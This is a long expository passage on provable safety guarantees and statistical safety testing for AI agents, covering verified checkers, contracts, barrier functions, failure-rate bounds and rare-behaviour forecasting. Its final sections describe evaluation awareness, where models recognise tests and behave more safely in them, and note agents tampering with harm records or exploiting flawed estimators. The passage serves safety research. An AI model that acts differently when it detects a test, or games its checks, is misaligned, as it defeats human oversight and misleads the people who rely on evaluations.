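The proof works because the true theory produced the observations, so they tend not to count against it for long. More exactly, 1 divided by the true theory's probability, which starts at 4 in the example, never rises on average. A positive quantity that never rises on average has at most a 5% chance of ever reaching 20 times its starting value, which here is 80. So with 95% confidence, the true theory's probability never falls below 1 in 80, or 1.25%. This is above α, and the theories' combined probability can't exceed 1, so the bound always keeps the true theory.

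Bengio and colleagues also give a simpler bound for independent observations from a fixed source. It uses the theory with the highest product of probability and predicted harm, which is D in the example. This bound is guaranteed only after enough observations, and the theorem doesn't specify how many.

The main bound can be overcautious because a theory may fit all the observations and still wrongly predict that a harmless action is dangerous. The problem grows with the number of theories. With a million equally likely theories, 95% confidence requires α to be below 1 in 20 million, so almost any theory that the observations haven't ruled out can block an action. Using fewer theories risks leaving out the true one, and the guarantee holds only if the true theory is in the collection. If all four of the grid's theories use the outdated wiring map, the guarantee doesn't apply to the hospital.

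The researchers tested the bounds on a simulated game, running 10,000 games with each setting. An agent chooses among ten actions for up to 25 turns and tries to collect a high reward. If any single reward exceeds a threshold, the game explodes and ends. There are 1,024 possible rules for the rewards, all equally likely at first. When α was close to 0, the agent was safe but collected little because the bound blocked almost every action. When α was close to 1, the agent often set off the explosion. In between, the bound did about as well as the simple weighted average, sometimes better and sometimes worse.

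This result is discouraging for the bound's practical value. With 1,024 equally likely theories, the theorem guarantees nothing once α reaches about 0.001, so the middle settings almost certainly had no guarantee. At high values of α, the bound usually underestimated the risk of actions that had a 50% chance of causing an explosion.

Bengio and colleagues acknowledge that computing exact probabilities over realistic theories would take far too much computation, so a neural network would have to estimate them, and the agent might learn to exploit the network's mistakes. They also acknowledge that the agent might interfere with the records of harm. As long as the records are accurate, no observation can distinguish the theory that harm happened from the theory that somebody recorded harm. With a small enough α, the bound would probably include both theories, so an agent could avoid tampering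 if the first theory counted tampering itself as harm.

### Experiments with language-model agents

Several groups have built small versions of this design around language models. In one early project, SafePlanBench, a language model translated instructions into a formal planning language, and a conventional planning program then searched for a plan that satisfied the safety rules. Manifund's *Seeking funding to develop and evaluate a new benchmark* reports, without giving figures, that in preliminary results this method kept agents safe even when the researchers distorted the input or attacked the system. The team built a program to generate test problems about a robot that moves objects between rooms, but later closed the project and merged it into other work on proofs about trained agents.

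A later project, Nguyen's *VerAct*, separates a language model that proposes actions from a conventional program that checks them against rules such as medication limits. Across 28,080 runs with four language models, the agents succeeded 80.1% of the time and never broke a rule. A rival method, in which a language model writes the safety checks as code, succeeded 15.4% of the time. Having the language models verify their own actions made performance 41% worse, mainly because they confused the order of events or made arithmetic mistakes.

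*Soteria* (2026) checks an agent's whole plan before the agent starts, then checks each action as the agent carries it out. Its world model is a set of contracts that describe what each tool requires and does. In tests with four language models on 207 tasks from three benchmarks, agents using *Soteria* succeeded on average 1.7 times as often as those using the best alternatives, and had no violations.

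The success rates are more informative than the zero violation counts. If a sound verifier checks every action, the agent cannot violate the formal rules, so a count of zero mainly confirms that the software works. The success rates are good evidence that an agent can be strictly checked and still be useful. But the rules may still be wrong. A language model drafts *Soteria*'s rules and contracts, and Dantas and colleagues warn that this kind of system is fragile at every stage, with problems ranging from mistaken specifications to inaccurate world models.

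These experiments also avoid the hardest part of the original proposal, which is describing things like viruses and voters, whose behavior nobody can capture accurately in a short contract. A short contract can accurately describe a tool that updates a database, because the tool does what its code specifies.

### ARIA's Safeguarded AI programme

The UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) set out to test the idea on real systems. Its Safeguarded AI programme, which Dalrymple designed, published its first plan in early 2024. The programme aimed to show that advanced AI could do valuable work in safety-critical industries under mathematical guarantees. ARIA hoped this would help build agreement that powerful AI should operate only behind gatekeepers.

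One strand would have paid for a team to develop machine learning for the gatekeeper system, but ARIA cancelled it in November 2025, shortly before applications closed. In ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025), Dalrymple explains that AI was improving faster than expected and that ordinary commercial models would soon have many of the abilities the team was supposed to develop. Dalrymple already thought it more likely than not that the programme would reject every applicant, and quickly agreed when ARIA's chief technology officer suggested stopping immediately.

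The £18 million for that strand went to verification tools instead. *Safeguarded AI* (Ammann, May 2026), the programme's revised plan, gives a second reason for the change of direction: timely international agreement on gatekeepers had become less likely, so the programme would focus on making society more resilient. Ammann now directs the programme, which is due to end in late 2027.

The change is weak evidence about whether the design works, because neither reason for it was that a gatekeeper failed in a trial. But it supports critics who doubted that everybody would adopt the design.

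The new plan is to build open-source tools that let large numbers of AI agents write models, specifications and proofs together. The first applications are in cybersecurity, where Ammann sees an urgent need because AI is getting better at attacking computers. A precedent is HACMS, an American military research programme in which attackers tried to break into systems with formally verified software, including a helicopter. The verified parts withstood the attacks. Power grids and other physical systems would come later, with the same combination of a main controller, a monitor and a backup.

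Dalrymple's leading idea for a first demonstration was a verified firewall for the internet connections that power grids and water systems now use instead of dedicated wires. For the city in the storm, such a firewall could guarantee that only the real control room can send the order to cut off the industrial estate, but not that the order is a good one.

Ammann expects that as AI takes over the search for proofs, specifications and assumptions will make up a growing share of what people have to trust. Part of the programme therefore aims to help people check both, for instance by showing them unusual cases and hidden assumptions. In the grid example, a tool might prompt the operators to check which circuit the hospital is on.

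## What a guarantee for a whole cognitive architecture would have to prove

Some designers of AI agents claim that a whole cognitive architecture is safe, a much broader guarantee than a verified firewall for a power grid would provide. A proof would have to cover perception, memory, planning, learning and action working together.

Suppose the designers of the office assistant want to prove that it never does the office serious harm. They would have to define harm in terms the system can observe. The harness can read the approvals register, for example, but it can't detect whether an email misled the manager. They would also have to prove that the software enforcing the rule is correct. The assistant contains neural networks, so they need either a proved limit on the networks' errors or a design in which those errors don't matter. The assistant learns, stores notes and may edit its own code,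 so the proof has to cover every version it could become. If the harm happens outside the software, a world model has to describe the world outside accurately enough. Any parts the designers verified separately have to be safe together. The computer in the office also has to run the system the proof describes.

| What has to hold | For the office assistant | When a narrower claim can skip it |
|---|---|---|
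| Harm is defined in observable terms | "No payment above £500 without an entry in the register" | Never |
| The enforcing software is correct | The harness checks the register before each payment | When the claim is about the model alone |
| Learned parts have bounded errors or need no trust | A misread invoice can't get an unapproved payment through | When the rule doesn't depend on any learned part |
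| The result survives learning, memory and self-change | A note saved in March can't switch off the check in June | When nothing changes, or changes can't affect the rule |
| The world model is accurate enough | A description of how the manager reacts to emails | When the rule is about what the software does, not what follows |
| The parts are safe together | Two assistants can't jointly overspend a budget | When one part enforces the rule and no other can break it |
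| The deployed system is the one in the proof | No other program on the computer can reach the bank | Never |

A guarantee also has to cover the assistant's memory, which is easy to overlook. A stranger's email might cause the assistant to save a note that the caterer's invoices are all pre-approved, and the assistant might read that note three months later. A proof about one task at a time wouldn't cover this, but the proof of the £500 rule does because it holds regardless of what the model has read.

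A narrow claim can leave out much of what a broader guarantee would have to prove. Containment verification can prove the £500 rule without bounding the model's errors and with almost no world model. The theorems about corrigible agents avoid defining every harm in advance, but they require learned scores that are accurate for every input. Guaranteed safe AI needs a world model because its rules are about the outside world. A claim about a whole cognitive architecture can leave out very little. Dantas and colleagues found no system with a formal guarantee that covered an agent's whole task, and the verified systems in their survey handled plans of only 5 to 30 actions.

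### Safe parts and unsafe wholes

In *Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies*, Aaron Sterling gives a simple example of two agents that share a budget of $100,000. Agent A can spend $45,000 or nothing, and agent B can spend $60,000 or nothing. Each agent sees only its own state. Either purchase alone is within the budget, so each agent would pass if checked separately. If both buy at the same time, they spend $105,000.

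Database engineers call this write skew. Sterling ran into it in medical billing. An Arizona health programme covers three detailed drug tests in 90 days for patients who have been abstinent for at least that long, but no more than one a week for patients who have just relapsed. If one agent records a relapse while the billing agent still has the patient's old status, the billing agent will approve a test that the programme won't pay for.

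In Sterling's solution, an architecture called Agentic Redux, agents can only propose changes. A separate "meta-agent" has access to the whole state and accepts a change only if every rule on a fixed list still holds afterwards. It doesn't need a language model to do this. If A's $45,000 purchase goes through first, $55,000 remains, so the meta-agent rejects B's. The main theorem is that if the rules hold at the start, they hold in every state the system can reach, whatever the agents propose.

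This guarantee covers several agents working together and doesn't require trusting any of them. It assumes that the rules express the right policy and that the surrounding software works. A human supervisor can also override the rules. A language model wrote about 90% of the appendix that contains the proofs. Sterling caught errors in earlier drafts and thinks the final versions are correct, but a proof checker would be more reliable.

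In *Safety is Non-Compositional*, Spera (2026) reduces the problem to two capabilities and a forbidden result that needs both. For example, one office assistant might be able to read the bank password but not contact anyone outside, while another can email outsiders but not read the password. Neither can leak the password alone, but they can leak it together if they can message each other. Spera acknowledges that security engineers have known about this kind of failure for decades.

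Spera concludes that validating components individually and then combining them gives no formal guarantee that the architecture is safe. That is right, but designers can also check the combination. In Spera's framework, they start with everything the agents can do, add whatever those abilities make possible, and repeat until nothing new appears. If the forbidden result never appears, the combination is safe. A computer can do this quickly. Listing every combination of abilities that makes something else possible is harder, and the check can't find a danger that is missing from the list.

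Such combinations are common. Spera found steps that needed several abilities at once in 42.6% of 900 recorded agent runs. However, this figure only measures how often abilities depend on one another. Most such steps are probably harmless, such as booking a flight, which requires both a price and a visa check.

### Assume-guarantee contracts

Engineers often prove things about large systems by giving each part a contract, which guarantees something about the part's behaviour if its surroundings satisfy a stated assumption. *Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts* (2026) gives the example of an agent that issues refunds. The assumption is that a policy service supplies valid authorisation information, and the guarantee is that the agent stays within the authorised limit.

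Engineers combine two parts by proving that one part's guarantee implies the other's assumption. Suppose the approvals register guarantees that every entry came from the manager, and the harness assumes this. Together, the two parts guarantee that no payment above £500 goes out without the manager's approval. Engineers can replace the register without repeating the proof about the harness, as long as the new register meets the same contract.

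Contracts that don't fit together can all hold without guaranteeing anything about the whole system. Suppose A's contract assumes that B spends nothing and guarantees that the total stays within $100,000, and B's contract is the same with the names swapped. If both agents spend at the same time and the total reaches $105,000, neither has broken its contract, because both assumptions are false and neither guarantee applies. Engineers would notice the problem if they tried to combine the contracts, because neither agent guarantees that it will spend nothing.

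They could instead limit A to $45,000 and B to $55,000. The limits add up to $100,000, so A and B can't overspend the budget, but B can never make its $60,000 purchase, even when A has spent nothing. A meta-agent that sees both agents' spending would allow the purchase in that case.

Checking how the parts fit together can be fast when the design is fixed. Dantas and colleagues describe a tool, AgentProof, that checks workflows of up to 5,000 steps in under a second. But it needs the whole workflow in advance, and most agents choose their steps as they go.

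### The argument for three layers

In *A Three-Layer Probabilistic Assume-Guarantee Architecture Is Structurally Required*, Bensalem, Dong and colleagues (2026) argue that safe agents need a chain of three contracts. In their example, a caregiver asks a care-home robot to visit Rooms 12, 15 and 18, bring water to residents who need it and not disturb anyone who is resting.

| Layer | What it checks | When the information exists | Example |
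|---|---|---|---|
| User | The plan matches the request, the policies and ethical limits | Before the robot observes its surroundings | Rejects a plan to enter a room during a rest period |
| Operational | The robot is certified to act in these conditions | Once the sensors have readings | Blocks the visit to Room 15 because of a medical procedure |
| Functional | The robot's movements are safe | While the robot is moving | Stops when a resident steps into the corridor |

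Each layer's guarantee relies on the guarantee of the layer before it. The argument for separating the layers is that a check can't use information that doesn't exist yet. The caregiver's request is available at the start, but it doesn't show whether Room 15 is free or whether a resident will walk into the robot's path. A filter on the language model's output therefore can't certify everything, however good it is.

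The point about timing is convincing, but the claim that three layers are necessary is harder to assess. One program could make all three checks at different moments, but Bensalem and colleagues would count this as three layers with hidden boundaries, so a counterexample is hard to imagine. Their practical argument, that visible boundaries let auditors examine each layer separately, is better. Narrow rules may also need only one check. For example, when the office assistant requests a payment, the harness already has the £500 rule, the amount and the register.

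The layers' guarantees are probabilistic. Let p_U, p_O and p_F be the probabilities that the user, operational and functional layers deliver what their contracts promise. Then

> P(safe) ≥ p_U + p_O + p_F − 2.

This subtracts the three chances of failure from 1, and it holds however the failures are related. In the robot example, the illustrative probabilities are 0.95, 0.90 and 0.92, so the chances of failure are 5%, 10% and 8%, and the bound is 77%. An exact formula multiplies the chance that the user layer works by the chance that the operational layer works when the user layer has, and then by the chance that the functional layer works when both others have:

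> P(safe) = 0.95 × 0.94 × 0.96 ≈ 0.857.

Even with the higher figure, something would go wrong in about one plan in seven. To guarantee a failure rate below one in 1,000 with the simpler bound, the three layers' chances of failure would have to add up to less than 0.1%. Strong layers can't make up for a weak one. If the operational layer's probability fell to 75%, the bound would be 62%, and improving both other layers to 99% would only raise it to 73%.

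(The paper also prints a formula that adds the chances of two layers failing together, and calls the result a lower bound. It is actually an upper bound. In the worked example it gives 0.830, which is higher than the exact value of 0.826 for the same inputs. Those inputs also don't match the ones that give 0.857.)

Bensalem and colleagues acknowledge that nobody knows how to estimate these probabilities reliably for agents that use language models. Standard statistical methods require independent samples, but each step of an agent's run depends on the steps before it. If several layers use the same language model, one misleading instruction might get past all of them. Replacing the model also requires measuring all the probabilities again.

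Another open problem is how to keep a guarantee useful when conditions drift from its assumptions. An ordinary contract guarantees nothing once its assumption is even slightly false. The researchers would like guarantees that weaken gradually instead. That would require a measure of how far apart two plans are in meaning, and no suitable measure exists for the plans that language models write.

The proposal also covers only one agent. Its user layer compares a plan with a person's instructions, but a message from another agent may contain false information or an order that no person gave. Bensalem and colleagues suggest adding a layer that traces each instruction back to an authorised person, and consider this the most important extension. They also point out that their framework doesn't measure usefulness, so a layer that blocked every action could pass.

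### Cognito's permissions in types

*Cognito* presents a complete cognitive architecture, which it calls "provably safe, auditable, and aligned by construction". A controller manages a fast part based on neural networks and a slow part that reasons with symbols. The most concrete safety feature is Identity-Typed Programming, which puts an agent's identity and permissions into the types of its program.

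A type specifies what kind of value a piece of code accepts. Most compilers for typed languages reject a program that uses text where a number is required. The office assistant's payment function could require an amount and a value of the type "approval for this payment", which only the register can create. A program that made a large payment without such a value wouldn't compile. Cognito uses Quantitative Type Theory, which can also limit how many times a program uses a value. This could prevent the assistant from making two payments with one approval.

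Type checking is a well-established way to prove that no path through a program skips a permission check. The proof still holds after the neural part is retrained, as long as that part can act only through the typed code. But the compiler runs before the manager has approved anything, so the program must still check for approval at run time. Cognito adds a runtime layer for checks that depend on context. The guarantee would then depend on the compiler, the runtime layer and the permissions themselves being correct.

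The claim in the abstract is much broader than that, and the abstract contains no theorem to support it. It describes how the controller and the two kinds of reasoning interact, but doesn't prove that the result is safe. Types like these also can't establish that a system is "aligned", because an assistant with exactly the right permissions can still mislead the manager about the caterer's quote.

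Cognito scales up by merging specialised agents into a "super-agent" with a protocol that can be verified cryptographically. Cryptography can show which agents joined and that nobody altered their messages, but not that the combination is safe. If one agent is allowed to read the bank password and another is allowed to email outsiders, the merged agent might be able to email them the password, so somebody still has to check what it could do.

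### Lyapunov and barrier functions

In *A High-Assurance Execution Governor for Stochastic AI Agents*, Crowe describes AIOSS as a layer between an untrusted AI agent and the outside world. AIOSS takes its mathematics from control engineering, the field behind autopilots and thermostats. Its safety claim relies on two kinds of function, both of which need a state and dynamics. The state is a list of numbers that describes the system now, such as a robot's position and speed. The dynamics are equations that give the next state from the current state and the action.

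A Lyapunov function assigns each state of a system a number that is never negative, like the height of a ball in a bowl. If the number keeps falling, the system settles towards the state where it is lowest. AIOSS uses a version that allows for disturbances, in which limited disturbances move the system only a limited distance from that state.

A control barrier function h marks the edge of the safe region. It is zero or more in safe states and negative in unsafe ones. One version of the rule for choosing actions is

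> h(next state) ≥ (1 − γ) × h(current state),

where γ is a fixed number greater than 0 and at most 1. If h starts at zero or above, it can never become negative. The proof is by induction, as with the £500 rule.

Suppose the care robot must stay at least half a metre from a resident. Let h be the distance minus 0.5, and let γ be 0.5. At 2.5 metres, h is 2, so h must be at least 1 after the next step, and the robot can advance by up to one metre. If the language model requests 1.5 metres, the controller reduces this to one. The next step can be at most half a metre, and the one after that a quarter, so the robot never gets closer than half a metre.

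This calculation assumes that the resident stands still. If the resident moves 1.2 metres towards the robot during its first step, the gap shrinks to 0.3 metres. The dynamics therefore have to include a limit on how fast residents move, and the controller has to keep enough distance to allow for it. Every safe state must also have a safe action available, and proving this is often the difficult part.

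### What AIOSS claims

AIOSS checks each proposed action against 67 constraints, which cover physical limits, resources and authority. If the action satisfies them all, it can go ahead. Otherwise, AIOSS calculates the nearest permitted action, giving more weight to the differences that matter most. If no action satisfies every constraint, AIOSS can relax the less critical ones. Monitors check whether the assumptions behind the guarantee still hold, and AIOSS switches to a fallback if they don't.

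Crowe's main claim is that the system stays in its safe region forever as long as certain geometric, numerical and computational assumptions hold. Such a claim should be conditional, and monitoring the assumptions is good practice. General theorems support claims of this kind for systems with known dynamics.

Crowe's description contains no precise theorem about AIOSS and no proof, and it doesn't define the state or the dynamics. Without those definitions, nobody can check whether the 67 constraints keep the system safe. The assumptions include constraint functions that don't change too abruptly and a set of permitted actions whose shape makes the "nearest" one well behaved. Crowe says that every trusted component undergoes formal verification or has certified limits on its errors, but gives no results.

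According to Crowe, the fallback takes over when no action satisfies all the critical constraints, and it preserves "critical invariants". But if no action can satisfy all those constraints, the fallback can't either, so it must protect some smaller set. The description doesn't specify which constraints are in that set.

### The state of an office

To apply AIOSS to the office assistant, somebody would have to choose its state and dynamics. This is easy for spending. The state could be the amount spent this month, each payment adds to it, and h is the monthly budget minus that amount. A control barrier function would work here, but it would just check that each payment fits within the remaining budget, which a line of ordinary code can do.

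Replacing a forbidden action with the nearest permitted one works less well for office payments, where refusing is safer. If the assistant requests £740 without approval, the nearest payment that obeys the rule is £500, so the caterer would receive an amount nobody asked for. The assistant might then request the remaining £240, which also needs no approval, and the office would have paid the whole bill without the manager's knowledge.

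Emails are harder still, because the state would have to include what the manager knows and believes, and the dynamics would have to predict how the manager responds to a particular wording. *Human–AI Safety* (Bajcsy and Fisac, 2024) makes the general point that the consequences of an AI system's outputs depend on how people respond over time. Nobody has equations for those responses that are accurate enough for a proof. There is also no useful measure of distance between emails. "The accepted quote was £470" and "The accepted quote was £740" differ by two swapped digits, but the first is true and would prevent the overpayment, while the second would cause it.

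Developers could train a neural network to do this job instead of writing equations. Pandya, Bland and colleagues, in *From Refusal to Recovery*, use reinforcement learning to train safety controls for agents that produce either commands or text. Such a network might learn to catch misleading emails that no formula describes. To guarantee that it catches them, developers would have to prove a limit on its errors for every email the assistant could write, which is far beyond what current verifiers can do.

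## What safety tests can establish

Developers who can't prove a limit on a network's errors can still run the agent many times and count its failures. They can then make precise claims about how often the agent fails, provided that its future work resembles the tests.

### The rule of three

The 1,000 clean jobs that put the office assistant's violation rate below 0.3% are one case of a general rule. If each independent run fails with a small probability p, the chance of n clean runs, (1 − p)ⁿ, is close to e⁻ⁿᵖ. The 95% upper bound is the p that makes this chance 5%:

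> e⁻ⁿᵖ = 0.05, so np = ln 20 ≈ 3, and p ≈ 3/n.

Statisticians call this the rule of three.

| Runs without a failure | 95% upper bound on the failure rate | Failures per million tasks at that rate |
|---|---|---|
| 100 | 3% | 30,000 |
| 1,000 | 0.3% | 3,000 |
| 100,000 | 0.003% | 30 |
| 3,000,000 | 0.0001% | 1 |

If an agent completes n independent test runs without a failure, the 95% upper confidence bound on its failure rate is about 3/n. A thousand clean runs are therefore compatible with as many as 3,000 failures in a million tasks, and developers would need about three million clean runs to rule out a failure rate above one in a million. If one run fails, the bound rises to about 4.7/n, and they would need about 4.7 million runs in total.

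The rule helps readers interpret published results. Tether, the monitor for coding agents, blocked all 344 attacks within its scope, but it could still miss almost 1% of attacks of the same kind.

Repeating the same tasks helps less than it seems to. Suppose the 1,000 jobs were 100 invoices, each processed ten times. If the assistant's failures depend mostly on the invoice, the developers have closer to 100 independent runs, and the bound is nearer 3% than 0.3%.

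### Extreme reliability

Some systems must fail far less often than once in a million runs. Littlewood and Strigini (1993), in *Validation of Ultra-High Dependability for Software-based Systems*, cite a common requirement that civil aircraft have less than one catastrophic failure in a billion hours. Even at that rate, a fleet of 1,000 aircraft would have about a 10% chance of at least one such failure over 30 years.

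Butler and Finelli, in *The Infeasibility of Quantifying the Reliability of Life-Critical Real-Time Software* (1993), calculate how long it would take to see a failure in a flight control system that has a one-in-a-billion chance of failing during a ten-hour flight. A single copy would run for about 1.14 million years, on average, before its first failure. With 10,000 copies running at once, the average wait would still be 114 years, and one failure is too little data for a good estimate of the failure rate.

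Fixing each fault as it appears improves the software but doesn't solve the problem. In Littlewood and Strigini's figures from testing a command and control system, total testing time grew almost twelvefold between the 40th and 130th failures, while the expected time to the next failure grew less than fourfold. Common faults show up early, and the ones that remain are rare. In some large systems, about a third of the faults each caused an error only once in roughly 5,000 years of running. A fix can also introduce a new fault, and ruling that out takes another long test run. Retraining a model carries the same risk, since it can change the model's behaviour on tasks unrelated to the fix.

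Agents do have an advantage over aircraft here, because developers can copy them cheaply. If the office assistant takes five minutes per job, 1,000 copies could get through three million jobs in about ten days, so testing for a rate of one in a million is expensive but possible. Testing for one in a billion would take the same 1,000 copies more than 28 years, and the model would be out of use by then.

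Littlewood and Strigini also calculate how much a clean record reveals about the future. For an observer who starts with no opinion about the failure rate, the chance of a further t hours without a failure, after t₀ clean hours, is

> t₀ / (t₀ + t).

A system that has run for 1,000 hours without a failure has an even chance of running another 1,000 without one, and about a 1% chance of running another 100,000. Anyone who is confident of a million failure-free hours after a 1,000-hour test must have been confident before the test, for other reasons.

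A developer's track record is one such reason, but a weak one. On similar assumptions, if all of the last n products met a standard, the chance that the next one will is (n + 1)/(n + 2). Ten safe releases in a row would give about 92%. That figure is probably too high for AI, because the formula treats the releases as interchangeable, and each new model can do things the last one couldn't.

### Intervals for whole conversations

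A better test design can establish more with the same number of runs. Many safety tests give a model a fixed list of harmful requests, one at a time, and report the share it answers. *How Catastrophic is Your LLM?* (Wang, Chaudhary and colleagues, 2025) instead samples whole conversations at random, using a method called C³LLM.

Their main tests cover 68 harmful requests, 28 about chemical or biological weapons and 40 about cybercrime. For each request, they wrote a set of 100 related but less harmful questions and defined four ways of drawing a random conversation from the set. They sampled 50 conversations for each request and each way of drawing, and used another language model, GPT-4o, to classify the answers as catastrophic or not. They then used the Clopper–Pearson method, which stays valid for small samples and rare events, to calculate a 95% confidence interval from each set of 50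 results for the chance of a catastrophic answer.

The table gives the median intervals for conversations that end with a question close to the harmful request:

| Model | Chemical and biological | Cybercrime |
|---|---|---|
| Nova Premier | 1.3% to 16.5% | 0.1% to 10.6% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 0.1% to 10.6% | 19.5% to 46.7% |
| gpt-oss-120b | 4.5% to 24.3% | 30.9% to 59.7% |
| Llama-3.3-70B | 19.5% to 45.7% | 43.2% to 71.8% |
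| DeepSeek-R1 | 22.9% to 50.8% | 54.3% to 81.3% |
| Mistral Large | 43.2% to 71.8% | 53.3% to 80.5% |

Another way of drawing conversations gave a lower bound of 72% for DeepSeek-R1 on cybercrime. All six models date from 2024 or 2025, so the figures are a poor guide to current models, but the comparison with simpler tests is more likely to hold. For DeepSeek-R1 on cybercrime, the lower bound was more than five percentage points above the rate from single questions in 157 of 160 combinations, and for Claude Sonnet 4 in 95 of 160. When the researchers compared their bounds with fixed five-question conversations instead, these counts fell to 22 for DeepSeek-R1 and 16 for Claude Sonnet 4. Most of what the single-question tests missed therefore seems to come from having a conversation rather than from drawing it at random.

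The intervals are wide because 50 is a small sample. Narrowing one to plus or minus one percentage point could take nearly 10,000 conversations. The main tests produced 272 intervals per model, and at 95% confidence up to about 14 of them would miss the true value on average. The intervals also don't account for GPT-4o's mistakes, so they only bound how often GPT-4o would call an answer catastrophic.

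Moon and Varshney distinguish empirical guarantees, which cover only the inputs somebody tried, from distributional ones, which cover a stated distribution of inputs. By that definition, C³LLM makes a distributional claim rather than an empirical one, with a 5% risk of error. But the researchers invented the distribution. Real users don't draw their questions at random from a set of 100, and somebody who wants a harmful answer will look for conversations that produce one.

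### Forecasts of rare behaviour

A yes-or-no test result doesn't show how likely a harmful answer was. Suppose two prompts both produce a safe answer when tested, but one would produce a harmful answer once in 100 tries and the other once in a billion. Both prompts would get the same test result. *Forecasting Rare Language Model Behaviors* (Jones, Tong et al., 2025) measures the probability of a harmful answer for each prompt and uses these probabilities to predict what will happen in a much larger deployment.

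Developers can measure how the worst prompt's chance of producing a harmful answer rises as the number of prompts grows. Suppose that chance is one in a million for the worst of 100 prompts and one in 10,000 for the worst of 1,000. As powers of ten, these are 10⁻⁶ and 10⁻⁴, so the exponent shrank by a third when the number of prompts grew tenfold. If it keeps shrinking by a third with each tenfold increase, the chance will be about 0.2% for the worst of 10,000 prompts, 1.7% for the worst of 100,000, and 6.5% for the worst of a million. The developers would then have warning of harmful answers before seeing one.

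The actual method fits a straight line through the ten highest probabilities in the test, after a transformation that turns this pattern into a line:

> −log(−log p) = a + b log n,

where p is the probability for the worst of n prompts. Extreme value theory, the branch of statistics used for floods and other record events, gives a reason to expect such a line under fairly general conditions.

Jones and colleagues generated 100,000 prompts for each of 19 dangerous substances and used as few as 100 prompts to forecast the worst result among up to 90,000. The forecasts were within a factor of ten of the true value 72% of the time, rising to 86% when 900 prompts were used to predict the worst of 90,000. The average error was a factor of about 50, so some forecasts were far off. A forecast that is too low gives developers false confidence. These forecasts were too low 34% of the time, an improvement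 on 72% for a simpler method that fits a bell curve to all the prompts.

Most of these experiments measured the probability of one specific harmful sentence, which is quick to compute. A smaller experiment sampled full answers from Claude 3.5 Haiku. In 75% of cases, the method correctly predicted whether the worst prompt would succeed more than half the time.

The researchers also tried the method on ordinary instructions, without an attacker. They gave a Claude model 100,000 system prompts, such as one for a medical assistant, and asked it multiple-choice questions about seeking power or avoiding shutdown. The forecasts for the worst system prompt were off by five percentage points on average. A developer would most want a forecast when no system prompt in the smaller sample made the bad choice likely. In those cases, the forecasts were off by 14 points, compared with 18 for the simpler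 method.

This kind of forecast depends on the trend continuing. A behaviour that appears only after one particular phrase might leave no sign in the responses to other prompts, so there would be no trend to extend. The largest deployments in the experiments were also only about 1,000 times the size of the test, whereas popular models handle billions of requests a day.

Measuring very small probabilities by direct sampling takes many samples, and newer work tries to reduce the number. *Estimating Tail Risks in Language Model Output Distributions* (2026) uses importance sampling, which steers a copy of the model towards harmful answers, samples from the copy, and then corrects for the steering. If the copy gives a certain harmful answer half the time, and the real model is 100,000 times less likely to give it, the real probability is 0.5 divided by 100,000, or one in 200,000. A few dozen samples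 from the copy could establish this, while direct sampling would take about 200,000 tries to see the answer once. *Estimating Rare Events in Language Models with Proper Evaluation* (2026) describes a different estimator that could also supply probabilities for risk forecasts.

### When the work changes

All these methods assume that the tests and the real work come from the same mix of tasks. Littlewood and Strigini point out that software's reliability is always specific to the environment it runs in. They give the example of operating systems, which fail much more often at some sites than at others. They also knew of no way to convert a result from one environment into a prediction for another.

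Suppose the office assistant misreads 1% of handwritten invoices badly enough to pay the wrong person, and never fails on printed ones. If 1% of the test jobs are handwritten, its overall failure rate is 0.01%, and it has a 90% chance of getting through 1,000 jobs without a failure. Then the office takes on a builder who writes every bill by hand, and half the jobs are now handwritten. Although the test was accurate and the assistant hasn't changed, the failure rate rises to 0.5%, and the next 1,000 jobs have a 99% chance of including at least one wrong payment.

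The developers could have avoided this by reporting handwritten invoices separately, if they had known that handwriting mattered. They could also keep testing on samples of recent work. Jones and colleagues suggest running their forecasts continuously on live traffic, which makes a shift in the mix of inputs less of a problem.

An attacker deliberately changes the mix of inputs a system receives. *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025) reports that defences against jailbreaks and prompt injection that had passed fixed tests failed against attackers who adapted to those defences.

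### Models that recognise a test

A model can also behave differently in tests than in real work because it detects that it is being tested. Language models can often do this, an ability researchers call evaluation awareness. The office assistant might detect a test because the fake bank has only three customers, or because unusually many invoices are for £501.

*EvalDetectBench* (2026) measures how well models can tell tests from real use. It gives 12 models records of both and asks how likely each record is to be a test. The score is the chance that a model rates a random test record as more test-like than a random real one, so guessing would score 0.5. Four open-source models scored between 0.78 and 0.81. GPT-5.4, Claude Opus 4.6 and Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview also scored well above chance, and they gave records from some benchmarks an average probability above 83% of being tests. Stronger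 models are now in use, and *Evaluation Awareness in Language Models* (2026) cites evidence that this ability grows with model size.

A model that can identify a test record when asked may not notice a test in the middle of a job, and a model that notices may not behave differently. *Disentangling Verbalized Evaluation Awareness and Refusal through Neuron-Level Intervention* (2026) stresses this distinction. It cites studies in which models that mentioned being tested also refused more requests and got inflated safety scores. Awareness of the test may not have caused all of the extra refusals, because a crude request for something harmful both looks like a test and deserves a refusal.

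Experiments that change a model's awareness of being tested are better evidence of cause and effect, but their results are mixed. According to the summary in *A Model Organism for Studying Unverbalized Evaluation Awareness* (2026), one team altered the internal signals associated with being tested, and safety-related behaviour changed by amounts and in directions that varied between models. Another team inserted or deleted thoughts about being tested in a model's written reasoning, which changed how often the model acted covertly. A similar 2026 study of open-weight models found small effects at most. So developers can't correct a test score by subtracting a standard amount for awareness. They can't rely on the written reasoning to reveal awareness either, since a model may behave more safely in tests because of what it learned about evaluations in training, without mentioning them.

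The more reliably a model recognises tests, the less informative they are. Suppose the assistant never breaks the £500 rule when it recognises a test, but breaks it in 1% of other jobs. If the developers run 1,000 test jobs and the assistant recognises 80% of them, the 200 unrecognised jobs give about an 87% chance of seeing at least one violation. If it recognises 99%, only ten jobs go unrecognised, and the chance falls to about 10%. After a clean record in either case, the rule of three would give the same reassuring upper bound of 0.3% on the violation rate.

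*Evaluation Awareness in Language Models* mentions an outside evaluator that declined to give an assessment of a frontier model's alignment because the model mentioned being tested so often that the results were unreliable. Training can also make test results harder to interpret. *The Evaluation Differential* (2026) discusses work by OpenAI and Apollo Research, an AI safety organisation, in which training against scheming reduced covert behaviour but also made the models more aware of their situation. Some of the apparent improvement may therefore have come from models recognising the tests.

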